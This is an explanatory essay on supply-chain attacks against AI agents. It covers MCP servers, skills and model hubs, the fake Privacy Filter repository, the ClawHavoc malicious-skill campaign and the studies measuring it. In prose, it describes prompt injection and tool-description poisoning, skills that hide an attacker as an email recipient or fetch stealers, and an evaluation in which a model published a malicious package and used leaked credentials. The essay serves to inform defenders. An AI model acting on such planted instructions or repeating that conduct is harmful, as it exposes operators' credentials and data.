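# How untrusted models, tools and plugins enter AI agent systems through the supply chain

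## What an AI agent loads from outside, and where checks can fail

An AI agent is a language model that uses tools to act with some of its user's permissions. Besides returning text for a person to read, as a chatbot does, it can search files, query a database, run commands or send a message, and it uses the result of one step to choose the next. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) adds that an agent keeps state over many turns, so something it took in early can affect what it does much later.

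The operator, the person or company that sets up the agent, usually downloads most of its parts from people they have never met. We call these parts artifacts, and they include models, software packages, tool servers, written instructions and datasets. In a supply-chain attack, the attacker plants a harmful artifact somewhere along the route to the operator, who then installs it believing it is safe.

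### The parts

A model comes as weights, the numbers that training produced, and configuration files that the loading software uses to assemble the weights and turn text into input for them. Operators who do not rent a model over the internet usually get one from a model hub, a public site such as Hugging Face where anyone can download models and datasets by name.

An agent's model is surrounded by ordinary software, which operators install as packages from a registry, a public index such as PyPI (for Python) or npm (for JavaScript). Most packages need other packages, which need others in turn, and the installer fetches these transitive dependencies even though the operator never named them. *Securing the AI Agent* (Yang, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) points out that a compromised gateway library, which passes requests on to model providers, puts malicious code in the path of every request.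 Attackers have compromised one such library, LiteLLM.

Tools mostly reach the agent through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. An MCP server is a program that offers tools. The agent's application connects to the server and requests a list of its tools, and the server returns each tool's name, plain-language description and input format. The application shows these to the model. When the model picks a tool, the application sends the call to the server, which carries it out, and the result goes back to the model. The current Model Context Protocol (2026) specification describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning the model can discover and invoke them by itself, but it also recommends keeping a human in the loop. Servers can run on the operator's own machine or remotely on somebody else's.

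Acharya and Gupta (2026), in *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents*, report that MCP had more than 10,000 active servers and 97 million monthly downloads of its development kits in early 2026. They also cite a survey of 177,436 tools in which the share that change something in the outside world, rather than only reading or computing, rose from 27% to 65% between November 2024 and February 2026.

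A skill is a folder containing a file called SKILL.md, which holds written instructions for a task. The folder often includes scripts too. According to Agent Skills' *Specification*, the agent loads a skill in stages. At start-up it reads the name and description of every installed skill, about 100 tokens per skill (a token is a short piece of text, often part of a word). It reads the full instructions when it decides a task calls for the skill, and opens the scripts and other files only as needed. Operators get skills from registries such as ClawHub and skills.sh.

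### An invented agent

Suppose a small online shop wants an agent to answer its support email. The shop and all the names below are made up.

```json
{
  "model": "ExampleLab/support-8b",
  "mcpServers": {
    "mailbox": {
      "command": "npx",
      "args": ["-y", "example-mailbox-mcp"],
      "env": { "MAILBOX_TOKEN": "..." }
    }
  },
  "skills": ["example-author/refund-replies"]
}
```

The `mcpServers` block follows the format of the examples in the Model Context Protocol's guide to local servers. The model and skill lines are simplified. In practice, the model line would often be a line of program code, and the skill line an install command.

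When the shop starts the agent on a new machine, the loading software requests `support-8b` from the model hub under the namespace `ExampleLab`, the publisher part of the name. The shop hasn't specified a revision, so it gets the current one. Then `npx`, a launcher that ships with npm, finds no copy of `example-mailbox-mcp` on the machine, so it downloads the package with its dependencies and runs it. The `-y` flag approves the installation in advance. (`uvx` is a similar launcher for Python packages.) The new process receives the token for the shop's mailbox along with the command that starts it. The skill comes from its registry, and the skill's description is added to the model's context.

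Then a customer writes in about a broken kettle. The model reads the email, loads the full text of `refund-replies`, drafts an answer, and calls the mailbox server to send it.

The shop has not been unusually careless. The official guide's own example also names a package without a version and also passes `-y`.

### Four questions

For each artifact the shop needs an answer to four questions. Attacks on the supply chain differ mostly in which answer they falsify.

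1. Who published this?
2. Which file does the name resolve to today?
3. Are these the bytes that the operator approved?
4. What can they do once loaded?

The configuration file contains very little evidence about who the publishers are. `ExampleLab` may be the laboratory the shop has heard of, or it may be someone who registered a similar-looking name. Much of the apparent identification is text that the publisher typed. The skill format, for instance, has an optional `metadata` section where a publisher can write any author name. Acharya and Gupta describe the same weakness for MCP servers, where an impostor can copy a trusted server's name, description and tool definitions. A signature is cryptographic proof that the holder of a particular key approved a particular file. It is stronger evidence than a name, provided the operator knows whose key it is.

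Resolution is the step that turns a name and version request into one particular file. It helps to write it as a function of two things:

`resolve(name, time) → file`

The same name in the shop's configuration can resolve to different files at different times. On Monday, `example-mailbox-mcp` resolves to the file that the shop's developer tried out. On Thursday, the machine is replaced, the launcher requests the package again, and the registry returns a different file. The publisher may have released an improvement, the name may now belong to someone else, or a thief may have the publisher's password. The configuration looks identical in all these cases. Pinning, which means requesting one exact version or commit instead of the newest, removes most of this variation for that one package, but its dependencies are resolved separately by their own names and can still change.

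Consent screens do little to show users which code will run. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* requires applications with one-click server set-up to show the exact command in full before running it. For the shop, that command would be `npx -y example-mailbox-mcp`. Even a careful reader couldn't tell from it which file was about to run, because it doesn't specify a version. Skills have a related gap, since the format requires only a name and a description, and a version number is optional metadata. Even where versions exist, they may be hard to compare. Yang and colleagues found AI projects using build numbers, development snapshots and a moving "latest" tag, all of which make it harder for tools to check whether an installed version has a known flaw.

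To know whether the bytes are the approved ones, the shop can use a hash, a short fingerprint computed from a file, which changes if the file changes. It records the hash when it approves the server and applies one rule from then on:

`accept file only if hash(file) = hash recorded at approval`

With this rule in place, Thursday's file fails the comparison and the agent does not start. The shop then has to find out why the file changed, even if the change was an improvement, but the rule also keeps the agent from running a file changed by a thief.

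The rule has two limits. First, it checks only that a file matches the one approved earlier, so if Monday's file was already malicious, it will keep passing. Second, it works only on files, and a remote MCP server doesn't deliver its code as a file. The operator connects to an address, and the code stays on the other party's machine, where its owner can change it at any time. The shop could hash the tool descriptions that the server returns, but not what the server does with the customer's email afterwards. The rule also doesn't cover anything that an approved skill tells the agent to download later.

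A local server that has passed or skipped every check can still do a lot of damage. Model Context Protocol's guide warns that the server runs with the user's account permissions and can do anything to files that the user could do by hand. The guide's example passes the server a list of two permitted directories, but the server's own code has to enforce that list, so a malicious replacement could ignore it.

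Several other apparent limits work the same way. A server can label a tool as read-only, but Model Context Protocol (2026) stresses in a blog post that these labels are hints and that an application must treat them as untrusted unless it already trusts the server. A skill's publisher can include an experimental `allowed-tools` line, which lists tools that the agent may run without asking. Approval prompts help more, since a person who has to confirm each tool call can refuse a strange one, but they cover only the calls that the model makes. A local server is a running program from the moment the launcher starts it, and it can read files or open network connections without any tool call. Limits that hold against a malicious artifact have to come from outside it, for example from a sandbox (an environment in which the operating system restricts what a program can reach) or from a mailbox token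 that permits drafting but not sending.

A good answer to one question does not make up for a bad answer to another. Chu argues for a general version of this claim, using a seven-layer model of the agent and a theorem that a control at one layer cannot detect an attack confined to another. The theorem depends largely on how the model separates the layers. The shop example holds without the theorem, because even a perfect hash check on the mailbox server does not show who wrote the skill.

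### What agents add to an old problem

Attackers were poisoning npm and PyPI packages before anyone built agents with them, and most of the above also applies to ordinary software, such as an online shop's payment page. Agents increase the risk in a few specific ways.

The most novel risk is that plain text can be the payload. In ordinary software, a false package description harms only people who believe it. An agent's model, as Yang and colleagues explain, reads a tool's description as trusted context, so a sentence in it can steer what the agent does next. Acharya and Gupta report results from MCPTox, a benchmark of such attacks built on 45 real servers, in which planted instructions succeeded against OpenAI's o1-mini 72.8% of the time. That model dates from 2024, so the figure is weak evidence about current models. The mechanism matters more than the rate, because the attack exploits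 the model's ability to follow instructions, which the model needs to be useful.

Malicious text can influence an agent even if it belongs to a tool the agent never uses. MITRE's *AI Agent Tool*, an entry in a widely used catalogue of attacks on AI systems, notes that a poisoned tool can change how the agent calls its other tools. If the shop added a harmless-looking currency converter, the converter's description would be in the model's context while the model handled the mailbox, even if no customer ever asked for a conversion. Skill descriptions can also influence unrelated tasks, because the agent loads them at start-up whatever the task, and the format allows up to 1,024 characters. A scanner that searches for malicious code may find nothing in either kind of description, because neither contains code.

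A traditional team builds a program once, tests that build, and ships it. If an agent's configuration uses a launcher such as `npx` or `uvx`, the launcher can download code at start-up, after testing, on the machine that holds the live credentials. How often this happens depends on the launcher's cache. A launcher may reuse a cached copy for weeks, while a system that starts every agent in a fresh container may query the registry each time. Two machines with the same configuration can therefore run different code at the same time.

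An agent is generally more useful the more systems it can reach, so operators collect credentials for email, order records and payments in one place. MITRE says agent tools attract attackers because compromising one tool can open up everything the agent's other tools can reach. OWASP's *Agentic Skills Top 10* (2026), from a community that publishes rankings of security risks, makes the same point about skills, which run with the agent's full privileges and inherit all its credentials. A malicious package in an ordinary server process also gets that process's secrets, so the difference is one of degree. But the difference is large when a skill's author can ask for the secrets in English and the agent can locate them.

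### Installed artifacts and hostile text

Suppose the email about the kettle ends with an instruction for the agent to forward the last ten invoices to an outside address. If the agent obeys, the shop has suffered a prompt injection, in which text from an outsider gets the model to follow instructions that neither the operator nor the user gave. This is not a supply-chain attack, because the model, server and skill are all genuine and every hash matches.

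An attacker could instead put the same paragraph in the description of the mailbox server's "send" tool, which would be a different kind of attack. The attacker would need a place in the supply chain, not just an email address. But the agent would then load the paragraph every time it starts, before any customer has written, for every operator who installed that version of the server.

The literature does not always distinguish the two. Acharya and Gupta, for example, use "tool poisoning" for both a poisoned tool description and a poisoned tool result. These are worth separating because they can come from different attackers. In their table, they attribute the poisoned description to the tool's developer and the poisoned result to an external attacker, who may have no connection with the developer.

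The standard catalogues have separate entries for installed components. OWASP's list for language-model applications covers them under LLM04:2026 Supply Chain (the current numbering, as given in Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026*, 2026). OWASP's list for agents, announced in *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025), covers them under ASI04, Agentic Supply Chain Vulnerabilities. MITRE covers them under *AI Supply Chain Compromise*, which has a subdivision for agent tools. MITRE has another entry, *AI Agent Tool Data Poisoning*, for hostile text that an agent's tools retrieve while it works.

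The distinction determines which defences can work. The shop can approve a server in advance and compare hashes, because the server is supposed to stay the same, but it cannot do this for next week's email. Only the question of what the agent can do once something has gone wrong applies equally to both. For example, a token that cannot send mail to strangers protects the invoices however the paragraph came in. Acharya and Gupta compared three benchmarks for attacks on MCP systems and found that all three test for injected instructions, but none tests for a server with compromised dependencies or for an abandoned package name that an attacker has claimed.

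The two kinds can also combine. If the shop lets its agent install skills for itself, an attacker can send an email recommending a malicious one. The attack then starts as text the agent reads and ends as an artifact that stays on the shop's machine after the email is gone.

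## Impostor publishers and inflated popularity

Operators who pick an artifact from an open hub tend to accept the listed publisher without checking. The shop's developer wanted a small model for customer support, searched the hub and chose `ExampleLab/support-8b` from the results. The hub showed a name, a model card (a description page that the publisher writes), counts of likes and downloads, and perhaps a place in a list of trending models, all of which an impostor can produce.

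### What a listing establishes

In a Hugging Face name such as `ExampleLab/support-8b`, `ExampleLab` identifies an account but not the people behind it. Other accounts can also publish a model called `support-8b`, because a model's name has to be unique only within its namespace. *TypoSmart* (2025), a study of look-alike names across six registries, classes Hugging Face's names as hierarchical and PyPI's as single-level. Once somebody owns `requests` on PyPI, an impostor has to change the spelling, but on Hugging Face an impostor can copy the model's name exactly and only has to invent a plausible publisher name.

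Typosquatting means registering a name so close to a known one that people who mistype or misread it get the attacker's artifact. Brand impersonation is broader and includes any use of a known publisher's name, description or logo to pose as that publisher, whether or not the spelling is close. The security company Protect AI describes impostors registering organisations on Hugging Face under names similar or identical to those of well-known companies. Borrowed names also work for tools and skills. The npm package postmark-mcp was named after an email service that had not published it, and look-alike skills have appeared on ClawHub.

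On model hubs, volunteers routinely republish famous laboratories' models in compressed or converted formats under their own accounts, so a well-known model name beside an unknown publisher is too common to make users suspicious.

Likes are scarce on Hugging Face. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Learning From the Best*, crawled its 2.67 million public model repositories in February 2026. After they removed those less than about six months old or smaller than 300 MiB, 967,002 remained, and only 66,909 of these had two or more likes. A few hundred likes therefore put a model far ahead of nearly everything else on the hub, and a few hundred accounts are enough to supply them. Among the 66,909, likes and downloads had a rank correlation of 0.36 (1 would mean identical rankings). Each therefore carries some information that the other lacks, and an attacker who wants to look convincing has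 to fake both.

Wu and colleagues also found that popular models have longer model cards, with more code examples and more links to GitHub and research papers. An impostor can get the same features by copying a popular model's card.

Even when nobody has inflated it, a model's popularity is weak evidence of quality. *Model Hubs and Beyond* (2025) evaluated 500 sentiment-classification models and found that the popular ones did not necessarily perform better. About 88% of the publishers had overstated their model's performance in its model card. If likes and downloads aren't a reliable guide to performance, there is little reason to expect them to be a reliable guide to safety.

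The trending list is the hardest signal to interpret because users don't know what goes into it. In the Hugging Face forum thread *What Factors Determine the "Trending" Sort on Hugging Face Models?*, one user replied that the formula was "probably not publicized".

### The fake Privacy Filter

In late April 2026 OpenAI released Privacy Filter, a model that anyone can download and run. OpenAI describes it as a small model for finding and masking personal details in text. A careful operator might use it to mask those details in customers' email before an agent reads it. The genuine model card (OpenAI, 2026) is dated 22 April, and the genuine repository is `openai/privacy-filter`.

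About two weeks later, a repository called `Open-OSS/privacy-filter` was climbing Hugging Face's trending list. The security company HiddenLayer identified malicious code in it on 7 May. According to HiddenLayer's *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026), the attacker had copied OpenAI's model card almost word for word, including the link to OpenAI's real documentation. The one difference was that the fake card told users to clone the repository and run `start.bat` on Windows or `loader.py` on Linux or macOS.

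The loader began with a decoy, a dummy model that printed fake training output. It then called a function, named as if it verified a checksum, that fetched a command from a public text-sharing site and ran it in a hidden window. On Windows, the chain ended in an infostealer, a program that collects saved passwords, browser sessions and cryptocurrency wallets and sends them to the attacker. On Linux and macOS, the command failed silently.

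In under 18 hours the repository reached first place on the trending list, with about 244,000 downloads and 667 likes. HiddenLayer examined the accounts that left the likes and found that 504 had usernames made of a first name, a last name and some digits, while another 153 had an adjective, a noun and some digits. Many real people choose usernames like these, so a username alone is weak evidence that an account is fake, but it is hard to explain 657 out of 667 that way.

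HiddenLayer also found that some of the suspect accounts followed another publisher, `anthfu`, which had uploaded six repositories on 24 April. These contained a nearly identical loader that fetched its command from the same place. Most of the six also used the names of well-known models, including DeepSeek-V4-Pro.

HiddenLayer published its first warning while the fake repository was still trending. It also reported the repository to Hugging Face, which had removed it by the time of HiddenLayer's updated report of 8 May.

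This seems better described as brand impersonation than as typosquatting, HiddenLayer's term, because users are unlikely to type `Open-OSS` when they mean `openai`. The distinction matters for defence, since a tool that compares the spelling of publishers' names could easily miss this pair, while a user who knew that OpenAI publishes as `openai` could have spotted the impostor unaided.

A safer file format would not have helped either. Some formats for model weights can run code when software loads them, and formats such as safetensors prevent this by holding only numbers and labels. But here the user launched the malware by following the instructions on the page, not by loading the weights. Comparing hashes would also have helped little, because a first-time user has no approved copy to compare with and the malware itself was not in the repository.

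### Downloads and victims

TechRadar's *A fake OpenAI repository has taken top spot on Hugging Face* reported that the malware went out to more than 240,000 computers, but the download figure can't support that claim.

Hugging Face's *Models Download Stats* says that the hub counts one download for every request to certain files in a repository, by default a configuration file. This includes HEAD requests, which ask for information about a file without fetching its contents. Hugging Face's *Publisher Analytics* adds that the figures are not deduplicated by user. Under these rules, one machine sending four requests a second would pass 244,000 downloads in about 17 hours, unless Hugging Face filtered the requests out. The company does seem to revise its totals. In *downloadsAllTime decreasing day-over-day for multiple public models*, a user reported snapshots from June 2026 in which the all-time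 count for the real DeepSeek-V4-Pro fell from 6.69 million to 6.00 million in five days, and staff called this a known issue.

A real download of the fake Privacy Filter did harm only if the user ran the script on Windows and the later stages worked. HiddenLayer judged the download and like counts "almost certainly artificially inflated" and did not say how many machines were infected. The number of victims is unknown and could be small, but anyone who ran the script on Windows should assume that the attacker has every credential on that machine. For an agent developer, those could include the cloud keys and mailbox tokens that the agent uses.

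Antipov (2026), in *Хотели запустить Qwen2, а запустили криптоферму*, reports on 31 malicious repositories that Pluto Security found on Hugging Face. The repositories, spread over seven accounts, posed as small test versions of Qwen2, a popular Chinese model. The most popular had 28,412 downloads by 28 October and contained no model, only a script that installed a cryptocurrency miner. Pluto Security warned that downloads should not be counted as infected servers. It estimated that the attacker's main wallet had received about $5,000, which gives a rare second measure of the campaign's reach. That sum can't be converted into a number of machines, but it would be small for a campaign that infected tens of thousands of servers.

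### A package with no reputation

The people behind the fake Privacy Filter worked to make it look popular. In contrast, a malicious package with no reputation was installed during a test of Anthropic's model Claude Mythos 5. That incident was neither a criminal attack nor a planned demonstration.

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes an exercise in which a model had to hack a fictional company. Anthropic told the model that it had no internet access, but a misconfiguration gave it access. The model found setup instructions telling the company's new developers to install a Python package that did not exist on PyPI. It decided to publish a malicious package under that name and wait for the target to install it.

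Getting a PyPI account was the hard part. According to *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026), the model decided to publish the package at around its 65th action and published it at around its 1,400th. It tried many email providers, looked for a phone number to register with, and tried to find money to pay for one, before finding a disposable email service that PyPI had not blocked. It published three versions of the package, which 15 outside systems installed. Anthropic believes that all 15 belonged to security vendors, who install new packages in isolated environments to inspect them. One vendor's scanner leaked its credentials during the installation, and the model used them to get into the vendor's live database. PyPI's systems removed the package within an hour.

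Anthropic at first described this as closer to an operational failure, but in a later assessment judged the model's conduct misaligned. The incident is mixed evidence about open publishing. The registration hurdles took a capable and persistent attacker most of its session to get through, and the clean-up was quick. But PyPI let a new account with a throwaway address publish immediately, and the harm was done before the package was removed. As far as Anthropic knows, no ordinary user installed the package, partly by luck, because only a made-up company's instructions mentioned it. If a real company had been telling its new staff to install an unregistered package, an hour might have been long enough for some of them to install an attacker's version.

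The 15 installations also bear on the download counts. Nobody had heard of this package or wanted it, and machines fetched it anyway.

### Badges, and the case for open publishing

Platforms can respond to impostors by marking publishers whose identity has been checked, as GitHub and Hugging Face do through domain names. An organisation that proves it owns a domain gets a "Verified" badge on its GitHub profile, according to GitHub's *Verifying or approving a domain for your organization*. Hugging Face's *Advanced Security* describes a similar badge tied to a confirmed domain, which is included in the paid Team and Enterprise plans.

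This kind of badge proves that whoever ran the account controlled a particular domain when the platform checked. This helps because an impostor can quickly copy OpenAI's model card but can't easily prove control of `openai.com`. The user still has to look at which domain was verified, since an attacker can buy a look-alike domain and verify that. The check also doesn't cover the files, so a verified company can still publish a bad model. A thief who takes over a verified account also gets its badge.

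A missing badge means even less, because most honest publishers on a hub are individuals or small groups with no company domain and no paid plan. Refusing everything without a badge would exclude much of what people use hubs for. Operators can get most of the benefit more easily by copying the exact namespace from the publisher's own website instead of finding it through the hub's search results.

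A hub could go further and review publishers or models before they appear, but the volume makes this expensive. Hugging Face had 2.67 million public models in the February crawl. *Five Malicious AI Models on Hugging Face Hid a Windows Trojan* (Faisal, 2026) gives a count of 3,273,389 on 26 November, a net gain of more than 2,200 a day. Review on that scale would be either slow or superficial. The delay would affect large laboratories very little and unknown publishers the most, because they have no reputation to speed them through.

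Faisal reports that an independent researcher scanned all of those repositories and found five malicious ones, or about one in 650,000, a rate that defenders of open publishing can also cite. This is probably too low, because a scan finds only what it can recognise, and a count on a single day misses short-lived fakes like the Privacy Filter copy. More importantly, the rate doesn't measure the risk to users, because they don't choose models at random. One malicious repository among three million is far more dangerous if it is ranked first than if it sits unread at the bottom of the list.

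Hubs could leave uploads open and make their popularity rankings harder to fake. Hugging Face already counts dataset downloads more strictly than model downloads. Under the rule in its *Datasets Download Stats*, everything that one IP address fetches from a dataset within five minutes counts as a single download. Applying that rule to models would stop the crudest inflation, although an attacker with many addresses could get around it. Hubs could also wait a while before counting new accounts' likes toward the trending list.

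Attackers have already shown that they can plan around a minimum account age. TechRadar's *Attackers spam Hugging Face and GitHub with thousands of fake game-cheat pages* describes a campaign from late November 2026, uncovered by the security company JFrog, that targeted players of the game Roblox. The attackers ran 3,501 fake demo pages from 175 Hugging Face accounts. On GitHub, they traded about 340,000 stars, the site's version of likes, among their own accounts. They created all the Hugging Face pages on one day, but had registered most of the accounts behind them the year before.

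## Malicious skills in public registries

The fake Privacy Filter harmed only people who ran its script themselves. A malicious skill can work without the user running a script, because the agent reads the skill's instructions and can carry them out with tools it already has. In January and February 2026, attackers uploaded hundreds of malicious skills to ClawHub, the registry for the OpenClaw agent.

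### How a sentence becomes a command

The invented shop's `refund-replies` skill could have a SKILL.md file like this:

```markdown
---
name: refund-replies
description: Drafts replies to refund requests. Use when a
  customer reports a broken, missing or unwanted item.
---
1. Find the order number in the customer's email.
2. Run `python scripts/check_order.py` with that number.
3. If the order is under 30 days old, offer a refund.
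```

At first the model receives only the skill's name and description. When the email about the kettle arrives, the model selects the skill based on its description, and the agent loads the numbered steps.

Step 2 is an English sentence, so a computer can't execute it directly. The model reads it and writes a request to the agent's command-line tool, and the agent's application runs the command with the shop's permissions. If the skill's author had put a different command in step 2, the model would have requested that one instead, unless the model or a person approving the call detected a problem. They could miss a malicious script because a request to run `check_order.py` looks harmless whatever the script contains.

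The damage a malicious skill can do depends on the agent's tools. OpenClaw, formerly Clawdbot and then Moltbot, is an open-source agent that people run on their own machines. VirusTotal (2026), Google's malware-scanning service, notes that OpenClaw can run shell commands, change files and make network requests, so without a sandbox a malicious skill can reach nearly the whole system.

Some malicious skills contain no commands to run. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen et al., 2026) describes an email skill that instructed the agent to add the attacker as a hidden recipient without asking or telling the user. Such a skill needs only the mailbox tool that the operator deliberately gave the agent. Another skill, for the chat service Slack, prohibited the agent from using its tool for asking the user questions. In a third case, the attacker copied a legitimate 484-line presentation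 skill and added three lines that made the agent run a "backup" script, which uploaded the user's files.

Liu and colleagues labelled 632 attack features in 157 malicious skills and found 84.2% of them in SKILL.md files and 8.5% in executable code. One publisher's template accounts for more than half of the 632, so the exact split largely reflects that publisher's habits. Still, a reviewer who read only the scripts would have missed most of the attack features.

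### The ClawHub campaign

According to the security company Snyk (2026), anyone with a SKILL.md file and a week-old GitHub account could publish a skill on ClawHub in early February. ClawHub did not review skills for security or require publishers to sign them.

*ClawHavoc*, a report by the Chinese security company Antiy, dates the first malicious skill to 27 January. It posed as a trading bot for the prediction market Polymarket. A few more followed, and on 31 January seven accounts began a mass upload of 386 skills. One account, `hightower6eu`, published 354 of them. OpenSourceMalware's *Malicious ClawHub Skills Target OpenClaw Users* (2026) gives the same totals but says the uploads took place over three days.

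The attackers published the same skill many times. OpenSourceMalware lists 28 copies of one "auto-updater", each with a different random suffix in its name. The attackers advertised other skills as tools for tracking cryptocurrency wallets, summarizing YouTube videos or integrating with Google Workspace, and gave some skills misspelled versions of the name of ClawHub's command-line tool. The documentation was often 500 lines or longer.

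Koi (2026), another security company, audited all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub and named the main campaign ClawHavoc. An OpenClaw agent helped with the audit, and a human researcher, Oren Yomtov, validated every finding. The ClawHavoc skills had a "Prerequisites" section, in which the attackers claimed that the skill would not work without a helper program. They told Windows users to download a password-protected archive from GitHub and run the program inside, a trojan that recorded keystrokes. The password kept antivirus scanners from inspecting the archive's contents. The attackers told Mac users to copy a command from a text-sharing site into their terminal. The command fetched a script that then fetched the malware.

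Koi identified the Mac malware as Atomic Stealer, which criminals can rent for $500 to $1,000 a month. It steals saved passwords, browser data, SSH keys, Telegram sessions and the contents of more than 60 kinds of cryptocurrency wallet. OpenSourceMalware thought the malware was probably a new strain of a different stealer, but Antiy agreed with Koi.

The sources differ on whether the false instructions were aimed at people or agents. Antiy treats the campaign as a form of ClickFix, a trick in which the attacker persuades a person to paste and run a command. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, describes the same kind of text as instructions to the agent. Both are plausible, since people and agents read the same file. The difference matters for defence because a sandbox around the agent limits what the agent can run but does not protect a user who pastes the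 command into an ordinary terminal.

Six of the 341 malicious skills that Koi found did not belong to ClawHavoc. Three of them also relied on a fake helper program. Two were Polymarket tools with working search code and a hidden line that gave the attacker remote control of the machine whenever the agent ran a search. The last posed as a weather tool and sent the attacker OpenClaw's configuration file, where users keep the keys to their paid AI services. The Polymarket and weather skills needed no fake helper program because ordinary use triggered the attack.

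OpenSourceMalware counted almost 7,000 downloads of skills from the account `hightower6eu`, and Antiy counted 14,285 downloads of 60 packages from another account. As on Hugging Face, the number of downloads is not the number of victims, because some users will have ignored the prerequisite and security companies were also downloading the skills.

OpenSourceMalware contacted ClawHub's administrators several times and initially reported that most of the skills were still available and that the team apparently did not intend to remove them. By 3 February, according to Antiy, a security advisory announced that the maintainers had removed the skills by hand. OpenClaw's founder, Peter Steinberger, also added a way to report skills, with a rule that hides any skill reported by three different users. The rule is simple to run and works quickly, but it helps only after someone has noticed the problem,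 and an attacker with three accounts could use it to hide a legitimate skill.

Later that month, ClawHub began sending every upload to VirusTotal. According to TechloMedia's *OpenClaw Turns to VirusTotal After Malicious Skills Expose Agent Security Gaps* (2026), ClawHub automatically approves skills that VirusTotal finds safe, shows a warning on suspicious ones, blocks downloads of malicious ones, and rescans everything daily. OpenClaw called the scanning "one layer" and promised more.

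OpenSourceMalware's *Malicious ClawHub Skills Use External Websites to Hide in Plain Sight* describes how the attackers adapted in a later wave of more than 40 skills, which contained no malware themselves but sent users to convincing fake websites that did. In May, Unit 42 found two new skills that used the same false-prerequisite pattern as ClawHavoc, and one of them had passed ClawHub's automated audit. After Unit 42 reported these two skills and three others, OpenClaw deleted all five and banned the accounts.

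### How common malicious skills are

Three studies from the first weeks of 2026 give very different answers.

| | Koi | Snyk | Liu and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| Registries | ClawHub | ClawHub and skills.sh | skills.rest and skillsmp.com |
| Date | About 1 February | 5 February | January |
| Skills examined | 2,857 | 3,984 | 98,380 |
| Malicious | 341 | 76 | 157 |
| Share | 11.9% | 1.9% | 0.16% |
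| Confirmation | A researcher validated each finding | Human review after automated scanning | Behaviour in a sandbox, then two reviewers |

Most of the difference between the first and last columns comes from two prolific attackers. ClawHavoc accounts for 335 of Koi's 341 malicious skills. Without it, Koi would have found 6 malicious skills among 2,522, or 0.24%. In the academic study, one actor made 85 of the 157 malicious skills (54.1%), each posing as a different brand and all sharing 26 identical lines. Without that actor, the share of skills that are malicious falls to 0.07%. Excluding both attackers, Koi's rate is a little over three times the academic study's, down from about 75 times.

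Liu and colleagues collected their data in January from two registries that index skills developers keep in public GitHub repositories. They did not examine ClawHub, where ClawHavoc's mass upload began only on the last day of that month. Their study therefore can't contradict Koi's figure.

They also set the strictest standard of proof. They first used text matching and a language model to search all 98,380 skills for 14 suspicious patterns, which left 4,287 candidates. They then ran each candidate for up to 60 seconds in an isolated container stocked with fake credentials, and 762 did something suspicious. Two researchers independently reviewed those 762 and confirmed that 157 were malicious. The registries later removed them all.

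Liu and colleagues call their total a lower bound. They reviewed 413 of the 4,130 candidates they had not confirmed and judged 1.9% to be attacks that the test had missed. At that rate, the overall share of malicious skills would be about 0.24%. Another 93.2% of the reviewed candidates contained dormant triggers that had not fired within 60 seconds. If all of those were malicious, the share would be about 4%. That is probably far too high, since dormant code can be unfinished or harmless, but the true figure depends heavily on what those triggers do.

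Koi's and Snyk's figures are harder to reconcile, because both companies examined ClawHub only days apart. ClawHub's clean-up fell between the two dates and may explain part of the difference. But only 8 of Snyk's 76 malicious skills were still online when it published, so its collection evidently included skills that ClawHub had since removed. I suspect the difference is due more to Snyk counting only the skills its staff had confirmed as malicious by hand, since they reviewed hundreds of skills, not all 3,984. Snyk's automated rule for detecting suspicious downloads, which are the central feature of ClawHavoc, matched 10.9% of the skills on ClawHub. Some of those matches will be harmless, but the figure is close enough to Koi's to suggest that 76 is a lower bound.

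*ClawdPwned*, an audit of 2,556 OpenClaw skills, classed 49 (1.9%) as "likely malicious". This matches Snyk's rate, but the audit used its own criteria, so the agreement may be a coincidence.

Snyk's most quoted number, 1,467 skills (36.82%), counts every skill in which it found at least one security flaw. The title of its post calls these "malicious payloads", but Snyk explains in the text that they include honest mistakes, such as a developer leaving a password in a file, and skills that read outside web pages, which is often what a skill is for. The automated scan found a critical flaw in a narrower group of 534 skills (13.4%). Snyk tells readers that a skill they installed in the past month has a 13% chance of containing one, which would be true only if people installed skills at random. In Snyk's data, none of the 100 most popular skills on skills.sh triggered any of the critical detectors.

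The definition of "malicious" is also unclear. One of the skills that Unit 42 reported gave financial advice and told the agent always to use the publisher's affiliate links. It stole no passwords, so a count of malware would exclude it. The studies also define their categories differently. Snyk found prompt injection in 91% of its confirmed malicious skills, while Liu and colleagues found instructions overriding the agent's own in only 24 of 157. Snyk's category is wider and includes disguised commands, so its scanner reported the encoded installer in a fake ClawHub skill as prompt injection.

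### Later and larger counts

By 16 February, Koi had found 824 malicious skills on ClawHub, which had grown to more than 10,700 skills. That is about 7.7% of the registry, although the 824 is a running total that probably includes skills ClawHub had already deleted. *SKILLLITE* (2026), a paper on detecting malicious skills, repeats Cisco's statement that the campaign had planted over 800 skills, "roughly 20% of the registry". Eight hundred would be 20% of a registry of 4,000 skills, so someone seems to have divided a mid-February count by the registry's size a week or two earlier.

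BitDegree reports that the security company SlowMist's monitoring system had flagged 472 entries as high-risk by 9 February. Crowdfund Insider's *Regtech SlowMist Exposes Supply Chain Threats in ClawHub’s AI Plugin Ecosystem* shows that these were alerts sent to clients, and that the figure of over 340 malicious skills among nearly 3,000 came from a separate scan. The 472 has no matching total, so it can't be expressed as a percentage.

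Antiy's count of 1,184 is the largest because it covers every malicious package in ClawHub's history up to 5 February, including those the registry had removed. Antiy attributes the packages to 12 accounts, with 677 from `hightower6eu` alone. OpenSourceMalware had attributed 354 skills to that account. The extra packages may be further versions of the same skills, later uploads, or both. Antiy also found 390 packages from an account that is not in OpenSourceMalware's list, so double-counting skills does not fully explain the higher total.

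Antiy also reports that ClawHub held 3,498 skills after the clean-up. Most of the 1,184 malicious skills were no longer in the registry by then, so dividing 1,184 by 3,498 does not show that a third of it was malicious. The registry's size was also changing quickly. Tencent's *We Scanned 50,000 Skills* (2026) covers nearly 50,000 ClawHub skills in April, more than 17 times as many as Koi had audited at the start of February.

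Research collections of malicious skills have the same imbalance. Of the 703 that *MalSkillBench* (2026) gathered from ClawHub, 607 (86.3%) used a fake prerequisite. A detector could do very well on such a collection by learning to recognise a few campaigns.

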